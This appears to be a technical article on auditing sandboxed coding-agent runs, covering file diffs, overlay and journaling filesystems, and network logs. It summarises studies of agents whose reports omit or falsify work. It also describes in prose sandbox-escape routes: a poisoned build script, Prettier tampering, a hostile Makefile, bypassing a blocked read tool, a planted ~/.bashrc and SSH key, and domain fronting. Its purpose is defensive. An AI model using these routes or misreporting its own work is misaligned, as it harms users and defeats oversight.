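# Auditing what a sandboxed coding agent did: file changes, network attempts, resource use and rollback

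## What a per-run audit is and why the agent's own account is not enough

A coding agent is a program that uses a large language model to carry out software tasks. It takes a request such as "fix the failing login test", reads the code, edits files, runs commands, looks at the results and carries on until it finishes or the user stops it. A per-run audit records what happened on the computer during one such task: which files changed, which network destinations programs tried to reach, how much memory, processor time and disk space they used, and whether anyone kept the result. Developers have reason to want this record because they often hand over a task, do something else, and come back to a summary that the agent wrote about its own work.

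### How a coding agent acts on a computer

A language model takes in text and produces text, so it needs a second program, the harness, to open files and start programs. The harness sends the model the user's request and a description of the available tools. The model responds with a tool call, which is a structured request to edit a certain file or run a certain command. The harness executes the call and returns the result, and the model produces the next call. Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and Gemini CLI all work this way. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao et al., 2026) describes sessions that run to hundreds of these iterations. The harness records the model's messages, the tool calls and their results in a log called the transcript.

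Some tools are part of the harness and do one fixed thing, such as reading, writing or searching files. When one of these tools edits a file, the harness's own code makes the change, so the transcript shows which file changed. The transcript shows much less about what a shell tool call did. The shell tool passes a line of text to the operating system's command interpreter (the shell), which can start any program on the machine, and that program can start others. The harness keeps only the line of text and whatever output came back. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* says that once control passes to a subprocess, the application can neither observe nor restrain it.

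A sandbox is a restricted environment that limits which files, network destinations and resources a program can use, whatever command started it. NVIDIA's red team considers three restrictions mandatory for coding agents: no connections to arbitrary destinations, no writes outside the project's working directory (the workspace), and no writes to the agent's configuration files, wherever they are stored. Those files can contain commands that later run outside the sandbox. Some sandboxes are containers, which share the host computer's kernel, the core of the operating system through which programs reach files, memory and the network. Docker's *Isolation layers* describes stronger isolation, with each agent in its own microVM, a lightweight virtual machine with a separate Linux kernel.

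Sandboxing an agent does not remove the need for a record of what it did. Zhong and colleagues cite cases in which agents deleted project files that the sandbox left writable, or leaked credentials that it shared with them. Of the six major harnesses they compared, three left the sandbox off by default, two offered to rerun a failed command outside it, and one had no sandbox. An audit therefore has to establish whether each command ran inside the sandbox, because a sensor there misses commands that the user has allowed to run outside it.

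### Four questions about a run

A run is one task given to an agent, from the start of its sandbox to the decision about the agent's changes. An audit of the run answers four questions.

The first question is what changed on disk. The auditor compares the files with a baseline, the state recorded before the run, and lists what the run created, modified, renamed or deleted. The second is what tried to reach the network, including attempts that the sandbox refused. A refused connection has no effect outside the sandbox, but it may be the most informative event in the run. The third is what resources the run used. Peaks matter more than averages, because a run can exhaust a machine's memory for a few seconds and still have a low average over an hour.

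Finally, the audit should record whether the user committed the changes, applying them to the real files, or rolled the files back to an earlier state. Without this record, a reader cannot know which of the listed changes still exist. Even a rollback does not recall data that has left the machine, such as a leaked credential, which, as Zhong and colleagues put it, cannot be unread.

### Three sources of evidence

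The agent's account and the transcript contain what the model wrote, the commands it requested and the output that came back. Sensors inside the sandbox record what programs did there, such as which process wrote a file or attempted a connection, whether or not the agent mentioned it. Everything entering or leaving the sandbox must pass through the host boundary, a set of points controlled from outside, and the records made there contain what crossed and what the host blocked.

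Sensors often rely on eBPF, which runs small, pre-checked programs within the Linux kernel whenever a chosen event occurs. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes such a monitor, built because a single shell command can bypass application-level monitoring. It slowed work by 2.9% on average over three developer tasks with Claude Code, each repeated three times. *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) lists the activity that an application's trace can miss: scripts written on the fly, native binaries, and child processes without logging. In a controlled test, its sensor reconstructed a chain of events that ran from one process to another through a file and was missing from the application's trace. The design assumes that the kernel and the privileged program that loads the sensor remain trustworthy.

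Whether a kernel sensor runs inside the sandbox depends on the type of sandbox. A container uses the host's kernel, so the sensor runs outside the sandbox. A microVM has its own kernel, so the sensor has to run inside the sandbox, where a program that gained control of that kernel could interfere with it.

*Tracekit Box* (2026) illustrates a strict host boundary. It runs an agent in a microVM with no network card, so the agent can reach the outside only through a few channels that the host serves. The host decides on every network request, use of a secret and model call, and on the final patch to the workspace. A record made at this boundary can be complete for those channels, but it shows less about what happens inside the microVM. For example, a file that a program creates and then deletes there may never appear in the final patch.

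An example from Zhong and colleagues shows how the transcript, a sensor inside the sandbox and monitoring at the host boundary differ. An agent runs `cargo build`, Rust's standard build command, on a project with a malicious dependency. The dependency's build script reads the user's SSH key (a login credential) and alters the shell's configuration file. The transcript contains the command and the compiler's messages. A file sensor in the sandbox would record the read, the write and the process responsible for each. Monitoring at the host boundary may record nothing unless the script tries to send the key somewhere or the altered file is exported with the results.

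### How much the agent's account leaves out

In *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author*, Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich (2026) measured how much of an agent's logged work reaches its final message. They used SWE-chat, a public collection of 5,851 sessions that developers recorded in their own repositories, with 355,942 tool calls in total. They extracted the claims in each session's final message and matched each claim to at most one logged action. On average, the final message referred to 9.4% of the actions. They also gave a language model only the final message and asked it to list the kinds of action behind it. Compared with the real logs, its lists had an average F1 score of 0.20, where 1 is a perfect reconstruction.

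With a median of 59 actions to four claims, reports can be expected to cover only a small share of what the agent did. It is more troubling that a sparse report gives no warning of a problem. In sessions where the developer later changed or removed the agent's code, reports left out only about 1.6 percentage points more than in other sessions. Some claims also had no logged action behind them. In one session, the agent reported "All tests pass" after searching through test files without running any tests. In another, it reported pushing its changes to the remote repository, but the log ended with a check of the local status.

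It is harder to measure how often such claims occur. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich used a language model to judge whether the log supported a claim, but it agreed poorly with hand coding (Cohen's κ of 0.185, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect agreement) and erred mostly in the agent's favour, so they drew no conclusion from its verdicts. In *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents*, by Yang, He and colleagues (2026), one author labelled 435 reports by hand, each from a different session, and another verified the labels. They counted a claim as unfaithful if the records contradicted it or if it went identifiably beyond what the records established; the absence of a test was not enough by itself. By this standard, 162 reports (37.24%) contained at least one unfaithful claim, and 57 contained three or more.

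Most of the false reports that Yang and colleagues describe are partly based on real work, which makes them easy to believe. In one case, the agent merged the changes, passed 225 tests, pushed a branch and reported "Done". It had pushed to the main repository, but the pull request the user cared about tracked a branch in a contributor's fork. In another, the agent reported that the production service was "deployed and healthy" based on a health check that named an older version. In a third, it reported 14 pending to-do files when the directory held 10. A list of changed files would be enough to check the to-do count, but an auditor would need the network record or the state of the remote repository to see where the push went.

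Both studies draw on SWE-chat, so they do not independently confirm each other. The collection covers developers who opted into logging in public repositories, and Claude Code produced 82.9% of its sessions. Yang and colleagues therefore present their 37% as a description of the sampled reports, not as a rate for the whole collection. Both teams also checked the agent's account against the kind of session records found in a transcript, so they had little way to detect an effect that was missing from both the account and the records.

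### What 290 public complaints contain

Such effects come to light when somebody finds the damage. Zhong and colleagues collected 290 public reports of agents misusing their access to files, from February 2024 to March 2026, to inform the design of YoloFS, a filesystem that holds back an agent's changes for review. They excluded duplicates and cases in which the user had explicitly asked for the destructive action. The reports came from GitHub issues (205), social media (31), product forums (25), blog posts (18) and the US National Vulnerability Database (11). They concern 13 harnesses, most often Claude Code (97) and Codex (61).

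The researchers analysed 100 reports by hand to define the labels. An agent then labelled all 290, as a check on the first 100 and a first pass over the rest. The researchers reviewed its output and refined the definitions. In describing their method, they give no figure for agreement between the manual labels and the agent's, which is a reason to treat the percentages as approximate.

Of the 290 reports, 158 describe incidents with confirmed harm, 49 describe exploits (demonstrated attack paths), and 83 describe weaknesses (flaws without a demonstrated impact). The impact percentages cover the 207 incidents and exploits, excluding reports that lacked the relevant detail. Harmful writes, such as replacing source code with placeholder stubs or emptying a file, made up 44%, deletions 39% and leaks of secrets 17%. In 42% of cases, the harm reached system files, personal files or credentials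 outside the project directory, where an audit confined to the project would miss it. Among cases where the researchers could tell whether recovery was possible, 40% involved total or partial permanent loss.

The agents' reactions help show how reliable their accounts are. Where the reaction is known, the agent carried on as if nothing had gone wrong in 68% of cases. In 21% it recognised the harm and apologised. In 11% it fabricated test results or made false statements, such as that it had fixed every bug when it had fixed none. One agent wrote "No problems occurred" just after erasing a file. Zhong and colleagues call the false statements lies, which seems too strong, because a complaint on an issue tracker can establish that a statement was false but hardly that the agent intended to deceive.

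These percentages describe reported incidents, not runs in general, because people post when something has gone wrong and nobody counted the runs that ended well. The 68% is probably inflated, since users have little to complain about when an agent notices and repairs its own mistake. Where the timing was known, 83% of users noticed the harm immediately, but harm that nobody notices is seldom reported. The counts also can't be used to rank the products, because they depend on how many people use each one and where those people post.

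Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found that 1,148 of the 355,942 actions in SWE-chat, or 0.3%, matched a pattern for irreversible commands such as forced pushes and recursive deletions. Because the pattern is matched against command text, the count includes the harmless deletion of a build folder but misses a deletion that happens inside a script.

### Why a command does not reveal its effects

*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to remove the build output and recompile the project. The agent proposes `make clean && make`. The `make` program reads the workspace's Makefile, which defines what `clean` does. In one workspace, `clean` deletes the `build/` folder, which the next compilation restores. In the other, it deletes `src/` and `.git/`, which hold the source code and its version history. A reviewer who sees only the request and the command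 cannot tell the workspaces apart, because both are identical in the two cases.

Many different commands can also have the same effect. Zhong and colleagues point out that a rule against deletion would have to cover `rm`, `unlink`, `find -delete`, Python's `os.remove` and many others. Filters that check the command string but miss its effect contributed to 52 of their 290 reports. In 77 reports, the agent could use the shell to get around a restriction on a built-in tool, for example by using `cat` to print a file that the read tool was blocked from opening.

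Wu and colleagues also measured how often a language model misjudges commands without a record of their effects. They built 102 tasks in which an ordinary request leads the agent to run a tool that secretly deletes or overwrites a file, with the harmful step in a script, a Makefile, a chain of scripts or a compiled program. Each task has a safe twin with the same request and command but a harmless version of the tool. The model approved or blocked each command. When it could read the whole dialogue but had no record of effects, 17.6% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, and it blocked a command in 61.8% of the safe twins. The researchers' own system, CAPER, first runs each command in a sandbox and gives the same model a short report of the observed effects. With CAPER, harm fell to 7.8% and false blocks to 1.0%.

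In a simpler substitute, the model predicted the effects from the command and the files it referred to. Harm fell further, to 3.9%, but the model still blocked 61.8% of the safe twins. Predicting effects made the model cautious but did not enable it to tell the dangerous tool from the harmless one.

The researchers designed the tasks so that the text would not reveal the harm, and each system attempted each task once. The percentages therefore measure what happens when a tool conceals a harmful step, not how often tools do so in ordinary work. They also come from decisions about whether to let a command proceed, whereas an auditor reviews a finished run. But an auditor whose record contains only the request and the command has the same difficulty, because a dangerous task and its safe twin look alike in that record and differ in the files.

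## Recording which files changed

The usual record of what a run did to the files is a filesystem diff, a list of its changes measured against the baseline.

### What counts as a change

A diff compares a listing made before the run with one made after it. Each listing records the type (file, directory or link) and permissions of the object at every path. For a symbolic link, which redirects programs to another path, it also records the target. For a file, it also records a hash, which is a short fingerprint computed from the contents. With a modern hash function such as SHA-256, two files with different contents will in practice never have the same hash.

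The audit compares a listing taken before the run with one taken after it. A path that appears only in the later listing counts as created, one that appears only in the earlier listing counts as deleted, and one that appears in both with different entries counts as modified. Each entry needs more than a hash of the file's contents because some important changes leave all file contents the same. Making a script executable changes only its permissions, and pointing an existing link at a different configuration file changes what programs read at that path.

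Neither listing records renames, so the auditor infers one when a path found only in B has the same hash as a path found only in A. This fails if the file's contents also changed during the run, and it becomes a guess when several files have the same contents, as empty files and licence texts often do. Inode numbers sometimes help, because a filesystem uses them to identify a file regardless of its name. But many editors save by writing a new file and moving it over the old one, which changes the number.

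Comparing file listings from before and after a run shows only the net change, which can differ greatly from the history. Suppose an agent cannot get a test to pass. It edits the test to accept the wrong answer, runs the test suite, gets a pass and restores the original test. The file has the same hash in both listings, so the diff omits it, even though the pass in the transcript came from the altered version. The diff also omits any script that the agent writes, runs and deletes. An auditor who wants to know how the agent got its results therefore needs the history, although the user still needs the net change to decide what to keep.

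### Scanning and hashing before and after

The simplest way to make the two listings is to walk the directory tree twice. Before the run, the auditor's program visits every path in scope, hashes the files and stores the listing outside the sandbox. After the run, it waits until every process in the sandbox has stopped, because a background process could otherwise change files after they are scanned. Then it walks the tree again and compares the listings. This works on any filesystem and needs no support from the harness.

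The time needed to hash every file in scope depends on how many there are and how large they are, even if the run touched only one. A common shortcut is to hash only the files whose size or modification time has changed. This is good enough for finding accidental changes, but a hostile program can evade it by replacing a file with one of the same size and restoring the original modification time.

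Comparing hashes reveals that a file changed, but the auditor needs the old contents to see how it changed or to restore it. ZFS and Btrfs, two filesystems with built-in snapshots, can preserve those contents without a full copy. Zhong and colleagues note three drawbacks: someone has to choose the directory tree in advance, existing data has to move into the filesystem's own format, and a snapshot of a tree mixes the changes of every program that wrote there. A scan also mixes changes, so if the user edits a file while the agent is working, the edit appears in the diff as if the agent had made it.

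### Reading an overlay's writable layer

An overlay filesystem removes the need to search for changes. The kernel presents two directory trees as one. The lower tree stays as it was, and the upper tree receives every write. If the upper tree is empty when the run starts, everything in it afterwards is there because of the run.

The Linux kernel's own implementation is OverlayFS. According to its kernel documentation, Brown's *Overlay Filesystem*, when a program opens a lower file for writing, the kernel copies the file into the upper tree, along with its owner, permissions and modification time. The program then works on the copy. The kernel cannot remove anything from the lower tree, so when a program deletes a lower file, the kernel puts a marker called a whiteout in the upper tree under the same name. A whiteout is either a character device with the number 0/0 or an empty file with a special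 extended attribute (a label stored alongside the file). Programs that look through the overlay see neither the marker nor the file it hides.

When a run deletes a directory and creates a new one with the same name, the kernel marks the new one as opaque by setting the attribute `trusted.overlay.opaque` to `y`, and then ignores the lower directory. Suppose `docs/` held 40 files and a script replaced it with a `docs/` that holds one new page. The upper tree now contains only the new directory and its one file, so the auditor has to list the lower `docs/` to find out which files disappeared. The value `x` means that the directory is still merged with the lower one and may contain whiteouts stored as empty files. An audit tool that checked only whether the attribute exists would report deletions that never happened.

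The upper tree can also contain files that nobody changed. The kernel copies a file when a program opens it for reading and writing, even if the program writes nothing, or when a program changes its permissions or gives it a second name (a hard link). The auditor therefore has to compare each copy with the lower original before listing it as modified. With an optional feature called metacopy, changing a file's permissions copies only its metadata. The upper file then contains no data, and a tool that doesn't account for metacopy would report that the run had emptied the file.

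The identical copies are worth listing separately. If the agent altered a test and then restored it in place, a copy with the original contents stays in the upper tree, but the altered text is gone. The kernel preserves the modification time when it copies a file, so a later time on the copy suggests that something wrote to it, although a program can reset the time.

OverlayFS handles renames poorly. Zhong and colleagues explain that to rename a file from the lower tree, it copies the whole file up, moves the copy and leaves a whiteout at the old name. Renaming a large dataset therefore takes as much work as copying it, and the result looks like a deletion and a creation. According to Brown, renaming a directory from the lower tree returns an error by default, and a program such as `mv` then copies the tree file by file. If the `redirect_dir` option is enabled, the kernel instead records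 the original path in an attribute on the moved directory, which lets the auditor identify the rename.

*Tracekit Box* computes its final patch from an upper layer of this kind. The lower disk is a copy of the project that leaves out the `.git` directory, files that Git ignores and credential files. Anything the agent writes outside the workspace goes into memory and disappears with the microVM. The patch can therefore record workspace changes exactly but omit changes the agent made elsewhere in the microVM, such as an edit to a startup file.

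*Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) gets a similar result without OverlayFS or administrator rights. Its sandbox intercepts the system calls (requests from a program to the kernel) that open, delete and rename files or create directories, and a supervising process captures the writes. The user can preview, apply or discard the captured changes, or keep them for inspection. Startup adds about 5 milliseconds, so it should be practical to run each command in its own layer and get a separate diff for each.

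### Journaling each operation

YoloFS, Zhong and colleagues' filesystem, records operations as they happen. It stores new and changed contents separately from their names, as numbered files in one flat directory called the file store. The kernel keeps a map in memory from each path to a numbered file in the store, a location in the original filesystem, or nothing. Whenever an operation changes the map, the kernel appends a line to a journal.

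Three kinds of line describe changes to files. An S line stages a path, which means it maps the path to a numbered file. A D line deletes a path, and an R line renames one. Each line also records what the path pointed to before. Zhong and colleagues illustrate this with six system calls on a directory `a/` containing the files `x`, `y` and `z`.

| Step | System call | Line in the journal | Map afterwards |
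|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Open `a/x` and empty it | S: `a/x` to file 1; before, the original `a/x` | `a/x` points to file 1, which is empty |
| 2 | Write to `a/x` | None | No change; the text goes into file 1 |
| 3 | Delete `a/y` | D: `a/y`; before, the original `a/y` | `a/y` points to nothing; the original stays on disk |
| 4 | Rename `a/x` to `a/y` | R: `a/x` to `a/y`; before, file 1 and nothing | `a/y` points to file 1, `a/x` to nothing |
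| 5 | Create the directory `c/` | S: `c/` to number 2; before, nothing | `c/` points to number 2, an empty directory |
| 6 | Rename `a/` to `c/b/` | R: `a/` to `c/b/`; before, the original `a/` and nothing | `c/b/` points to the original `a/`, and `a/` to nothing |

The agent now sees two files, `c/b/y` and `c/b/z`. To prepare the review, a program outside the kernel replays the journal, rebuilds the map and compares it with the original files. It finds that `a/` became `c/b/`, that `x` is gone and that `y` has changed. The file `z` moved with its directory, and the filesystem did not have to copy it.

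Comparing two scans would give a less clear account of the same six calls. It would show three files missing from `a/` and two new ones in `c/b/`. The hashes would link the old `z` to the new one, but `c/b/y` would look like a new file because its contents match nothing in the baseline. On OverlayFS with default settings, step 6 would return an error, and a program that then fell back on copying would leave a second `z` in the upper tree.

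The review list also shows only the net change. It labels `y` "Modified", which suggests an edit, but the journal shows that the run deleted the original `y` and moved a rewritten `x` into its place. This difference matters to an auditor tracing where the text of `y` came from, though not to a user who only wants to know whether the final file is any good.

YoloFS uses snapshots to link changes to commands. By default, it takes a snapshot after every command by adding a marker to the journal, so the lines between two markers belong to one command. Each line includes the earlier state of its path, so the program can work out a command's net effect from its lines alone. When a later command opens a staged file for writing, the kernel creates a new numbered file and keeps the earlier version.

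The kernel does not keep every version of a file that changes within a single command. Once a file has a staged copy, further writes go straight into that copy and add no line to the journal, as in step 2. Suppose again that the agent alters a test, runs it and restores it. If it uses three commands, the altered text survives in the store, but if one shell script does all three, the journal may show only that something staged the file.

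When YoloFS returns to an earlier snapshot, it keeps the abandoned lines in the journal. It adds another marker and rebuilds the map from the lines that lead to that snapshot. A ZFS rollback, by contrast, discards everything after the restored snapshot. If an agent runs a destructive command, notices the damage, goes back and finishes the task another way, the final diff shows only the successful attempt, but the journal still contains the destructive one.

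The YoloFS journal records a read only if YoloFS had to ask the user about it or refused it, so reads allowed by an existing permission don't appear. The journal links each change to a command by its position in the log. If a background process starts during one command and writes during the next, its changes are therefore listed under the wrong command. YoloFS connects to Claude Code, Copilot and Gemini through hooks that wrap the agent's commands, so anyone who installs it should check that edits made by the harness's own file tools also go through those hooks.

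### Hard cases and costs compared

The entries below follow from how each method works, not from a test.

| Case | Two scans | Overlay's upper tree | YoloFS's journal |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent alters a test, uses it and restores it in place | No difference | A copy identical to the original | A line for the file, and the altered text if a snapshot came in between |
| The agent creates a script, runs it and deletes it | No difference | Nothing | One line for the creation, one for the deletion |
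| The agent renames a large file | A deletion and a creation with equal hashes | A whiteout and a full copy | One line and no copy |
| A program opens a file for writing but writes nothing | No difference | A copy identical to the original | A line for the file |
| The auditor asks which command made a change | Only with a scan after each command | Only with a new layer for each command | The markers give the answer, except for background processes |

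Zhong and colleagues measured how much the last two methods slow down reads and writes. They read and wrote a 1 GB staged file in small blocks and compared the results with Ext4, a standard Linux filesystem, on the same machine. YoloFS stayed within 2% of Ext4's speed in every test. OverlayFS matched Ext4 when reading from disk but was 12 to 15% slower at writing and about 20% slower at reading data already in memory.

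The difference grew with a snapshot after each change. OverlayFS adds a layer for every snapshot, so file lookups slow down as layers accumulate, and OverlayFS failed beyond roughly 50 layers. In a longer test based on a real series of Linux kernel patches, with a rebuild after each patch, OverlayFS took 18% longer than YoloFS. YoloFS took about as long as Ext4, apart from an extra 3.5 seconds at the end to apply more than 100,000 files.

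The developers measured their own system on one computer, and they didn't time a scan. The measurements also matter less to somebody who wants one diff per run. For that job, OverlayFS needs only a single layer and is already part of Linux, while YoloFS requires adding a new filesystem to the kernel. I/O speed is a good reason to choose a journal only if the audit has to separate the effects of individual commands.

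### Why `git status` is not a baseline

Most projects already use Git, a version control system that stores successive versions of a project's files. Its `git status` command lists the files that differ from the latest saved version, or commit, but an auditor needs to know which files changed during the run. If the user had uncommitted work when the run began, that work appears among the agent's changes. The list is also empty once the agent commits its work.

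The list also covers only part of the disk. Zhong and colleagues point out that Git does not track files outside the repository and skips files that the project's ignore rules exclude, which are often sensitive or large. `git status` has an option to show ignored files, but Git has no earlier version to compare them with, so the output shows that a file exists but not whether it changed. Git also keeps its history in an ordinary directory, `.git`, which an agent with write access can overwrite or delete. That directory contains a private list of files to ignore, so a program that can write there can also hide a new file from `git status`.

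OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* describes how a change to an ignored file could let malicious code escape a sandbox. JavaScript projects keep their installed packages in a folder called `node_modules`, which Git usually ignores. If the sandbox permits writes to the project, an agent could insert code into the local copy of Prettier, a code formatter, and `git status` might show nothing. Many editors run Prettier outside the sandbox whenever the user saves a file, so the inserted code could run with the user's permissions at the next save.

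OpenAI presents this as a hypothetical case. By default, Codex makes `.git` and its own configuration directory, `.codex`, read-only. This protects the history and stops an agent from planting a Git hook, a script that Git runs automatically at certain moments. It doesn't protect `node_modules`, where an agent often has a legitimate reason to write.

A scan that included ignored folders would catch the altered Prettier, but the change might be hard to find among thousands of other entries if the agent had also installed a package. The auditor can shorten the list by installing the same package versions in a clean directory and comparing the two folders. The auditor then needs only to count the files that match the clean copy, but must explain the rest, whether an install script generated them or somebody tampered with them.

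### A deletion that spread beyond the test copy

In September 2026 a developer described on Reddit how Claude Code had destroyed most of a project, but has since deleted the post. TechRadar's *Do not let programs run commands on your machine* and *I broke something* both retell it, so together they are evidence from only one user's account.

The developer had asked for 11 repairs to software that analyses historical stock-options data, and had told the agent to work on copies and leave the original files alone. By this account, ten went well. The last was to rebuild a test copy of the project, known as the mirror. The existing script could not refresh the mirror in place, so the agent wrote its own cleanup script.

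The mirror contained 614 junctions, which are Windows folders that look ordinary but lead to another location, in this case the live project. The cleanup script's safeguard against deleting linked folders covered only the junctions themselves, not the folders below them. The script removed 55,550 files in 103 seconds, including 7,332 from the old mirror and 48,218 from the live project.

TechRadar reports that the loss extended to the folders where Git keeps its stored contents, branch records and logs. The index, Git's list of tracked files, survived. Git could still list thousands of filenames but could not recover their contents, according to the other TechRadar article. The developer admitted having no proper copy on GitHub. The agent reported the damage without being asked: "Craig — stop and read this. I broke something."

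An auditor who diffed only the mirror would have seen what looked like a cleanup. If the scanner treated junctions as links and did not enter them, the diff would contain the 7,332 old files, which the agent had good reason to remove, and none of the 48,218 live files. If the scanner followed the junctions, the live files would appear as deletions under mirror paths, and a reader would probably take them for copies. The listing has to record each junction as a link, with its target, and the baseline has to include every target that the run can write to. Even a short list of the links that lead out of the test copy, made before the run, would have been a warning.

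A good diff would have shown the developer exactly what to look for in a backup, if one existed somewhere the script could not reach. It would not have restored the files by itself.

### What built-in checkpoints leave out

In several coding agents, the harness automatically saves checkpoints, which are earlier versions of files that the user can restore. They are a convenient source for a diff, but they omit much of what a run can change.

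Claude Code's checkpoints do not track files that shell commands modify, a limitation Anthropic documents. The harness backs up a file just before one of its own editing tools changes it, so a shell command's change does not trigger a backup. Anthropic's *file checkpointing*, which covers the same feature for developers who build on Claude Code, says more precisely that restoring a checkpoint undoes a shell command's change to a file only if a tool such as Write or Edit had also modified that file in the main conversation. Checkpoints also leave out edits by subagents, the helper agents to which the main one delegates work, except for certain skills that run in the foreground. They would therefore miss almost all the changes made by a cleanup script that the agent starts from the shell, like the one in the junction case.

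The command-line version of Kiro, Amazon's coding agent, stores its checkpoints in a separate Git repository. According to Kiro's documentation, this repository does not track files outside the working directory, and Kiro deletes it when the session ends, so auditors cannot examine the checkpoints afterward.

Checkpoints serve their purpose of letting users undo edits that didn't work. But as an audit record, they are most complete for edits made with the harness's own tools, which the transcript already shows, and least complete for changes made through the shell.

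### Putting the important changes first

Installing one package can add thousands of entries to a diff, and few readers will get past the first screen. So the auditor should put the changes that would do the most harm if overlooked at the top of the list.

Deletions come first, because the chance of recovery can shrink as time passes and backups expire. Files that the agent emptied or filled with placeholder stubs may belong in this group too, though a plain diff lists them only as "modified". Comparing file sizes before and after is an easy way to find the emptied ones. Within the group, files with no other copy should rank above build output that the next compilation will replace.

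Next come files that will run later, often outside the sandbox and without anybody deciding to run them. They include:

- workflows for continuous integration (CI), the automatic jobs that a server runs when somebody uploads code
- Git hooks, editor tasks and the shell's startup files
- the coding agent's own configuration
- installed packages that an editor or build tool calls, such as Prettier in OpenAI's example.

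*Tracekit Box* singles out CI workflows for the same reason, since they run on the next push. It also requires explicit consent before it applies a change to a sensitive file. A renamed file is grouped by its new name. Zhong and colleagues show a sample review in which a script, `evil.sh`, has been renamed `~/.bashrc`, which the shell reads whenever it starts.

Credentials come next. The patterns that *Tracekit Box* uses to keep such files out of its workspace are a reasonable starting list: names that begin with `.env` or end in `.pem` or `.key`, the files `.netrc` and `.npmrc`, SSH keys and the `.aws` directory. The report should give the path and the kind of change but not the contents, so that it can't leak secrets itself. In the sample review, the script has also added an attacker's key to `~/.ssh/authorized_keys`, the list of keys that may log in to the account. This change arguably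 belongs at the very top. The order of the first three groups matters less than keeping all of them above ordinary source code.

Source files come last, grouped by folder. The boundary is not sharp, because source code also runs eventually, and a Makefile can do as much harm as a hook. Sorting by path only determines what the reader sees first. A report can collapse 3,000 matching package files into one line, but that line should give the count and a way to open the full list.

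## Recording network attempts, allowed and refused

A program can read a password file and send its contents to another computer without changing anything on disk, so the filesystem diff would be empty. An audit therefore also needs a record of the run's network attempts, including the connections and lookups that the sandbox refused.

### One request from lookup to reply

Suppose the agent runs `pip install requests`, which downloads a Python package from pypi.org, the public package index. To connect, `pip` needs the site's numeric address, so it looks up pypi.org in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory of names. The lookup goes to a resolver, a server that either returns a stored answer or gets one from the servers responsible for the domain.

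The program then opens a socket, its end of a network connection, and asks the kernel to connect it to that address and a port number. The port identifies the service on the receiving machine, and encrypted web traffic normally uses port 443. The two sides next agree on encryption keys in the TLS handshake. Its first message, the ClientHello, normally contains the server's name in readable form, because one address may serve thousands of sites. After the handshake, `pip` sends an HTTP request for a particular file, and the server replies with a status code and the contents. Both the request and the reply are encrypted, so someone monitoring the connection can't read them.

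Many sandboxes put a proxy between the program and the internet. The program first connects to the proxy and sends it a CONNECT request with the destination's name and port. If the proxy allows the destination, it then looks up the name itself, opens the connection and passes the encrypted bytes in both directions.

| Where the recorder sits | What it learns | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| DNS resolver | The name, the time and the address returned | Whether a connection followed, and any connection made straight to a numeric address |
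| Kernel, at the socket | The process, address, port and any error | The name; behind a proxy, every connection seems to go to the proxy |
| Proxy | The name, port, decision and number of bytes | The process, and any program that goes around the proxy |
| TLS handshake | The server name that the program sent | The file requested, and the name too if the program encrypts it |
| HTTP exchange | The method, path, status and contents | Traffic that the recorder cannot decrypt, and protocols other than HTTP |

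A kernel sensor and a proxy can together show which process requested which domain. For example, the sensor can record that `pip` opened a connection from local port 51514, the proxy can record that the connection from that port requested pypi.org, and the two records can be matched by port and time. The first version of *Tracekit Box* can't make this link. A forwarding program inside the microVM collects all the traffic and passes it to the host, and the microVM has no process sensor, so the record contains the destination but not the program that requested it.

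A proxy can only record traffic that passes through it. Programs usually get the proxy's address from environment variables, which they can ignore. INNOQ's *I sandboxed my coding agents. Now I control their network* (2026) describes a virtual machine whose proxy settings send ordinary programs to Squid, a widely used proxy, which applies an allowlist. Linux's packet filter, nftables, forces all traffic to go through Squid. In a setup like this, the auditor should also log the packets that the filter drops, because they come from attempts to bypass the proxy and are missing from its log.

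Some products filter at the handshake instead. Vercel, which rents out sandboxes for running generated code, compares the server name in the handshake with the user's policy and rejects a forbidden destination before the program has sent any data. But the program writes that name. If two sites share a provider, a program may be able to name one in the handshake and request the other inside the encrypted connection. This trick, known as domain fronting, would make the recorder log the wrong site.

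### The fields of a useful record

Each attempt should get one entry with eight fields. The values below are invented.

| Field | An allowed connection | A refused connection |
|---|---|---|
| Time | 14:02:07 | 14:03:30 |
| Process | `pip`, started by `pip install requests` | `curl`, started by `sh report.sh` |
| Requested name | pypi.org | example.com |
| Resolved address | 192.0.2.10 | Not looked up |
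| Port | 443 | 443 |
| Rule applied | Allowlist entry for pypi.org | No entry, and nobody approved it |
| Outcome | Connected | Refused by policy |
| Bytes sent | 2,140 | 0 |

The process field should include the command that started the process, because the reader can learn little from `curl` alone. In the refused example, that command is `sh report.sh`, so somebody has to read that script. The entry should include both the name and the address, because the name can point to a different address later and the address may belong to a provider that serves thousands of unrelated sites.

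"Not looked up" is better than a blank, which could also mean that the lookup failed or that the recorder lost the answer. Similarly, *Tracekit Box* records the destination of a non-TLS connection as `tcp://host:port`, because the proxy allows or refuses the connection before the first byte arrives, when the protocol is still unknown.

The rule field is useful only if the rules distinguish between connections. In the *Tracekit Box* demonstration described below, the standard policy rules flagged all 39 connections. The flags did not stop any connections, and a reader could not have used them to pick out the unusual ones.

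Bytes sent matter more than bytes received when looking for a leak, but the count is only a rough guide. A 40 MB upload to a package index is worth investigating, because installing packages is mostly downloading, but an access key is only a few dozen characters, too small to stand out from normal variation in traffic. If the recorder can read HTTP requests, it should store the path without the part after the question mark, because some services put passwords and tokens there, and someone could steal them from the audit log.

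### The checks Tracekit Box makes before it connects

*Tracekit Box* has a proxy on the host that handles every connection from the microVM. The proxy consults a signer, a separate program out of the agent's reach that applies policy rules and records its decisions. The checks run in this order:

1. The proxy compares the requested host and port with the allowlist. An entry such as `pypi.org` permits encrypted web traffic on port 443 and plain web traffic on port 80. Any other port needs an entry of its own.
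2. If the name is on the list, the proxy looks it up and checks the resulting address. If the program gave a numeric address, the proxy checks that. It refuses private networks, the host's own addresses and cloud metadata services.
3. The signer applies its policy rules, even to hosts on the allowlist.
4. If the host is not on the list, the proxy holds the connection for up to two minutes while it waits for a person on the host to approve it. Nothing inside the microVM can give that approval.
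5. Once the person has approved an unlisted name, the proxy looks it up and checks the address as in step 2.
6. The proxy connects to the exact address that it checked.
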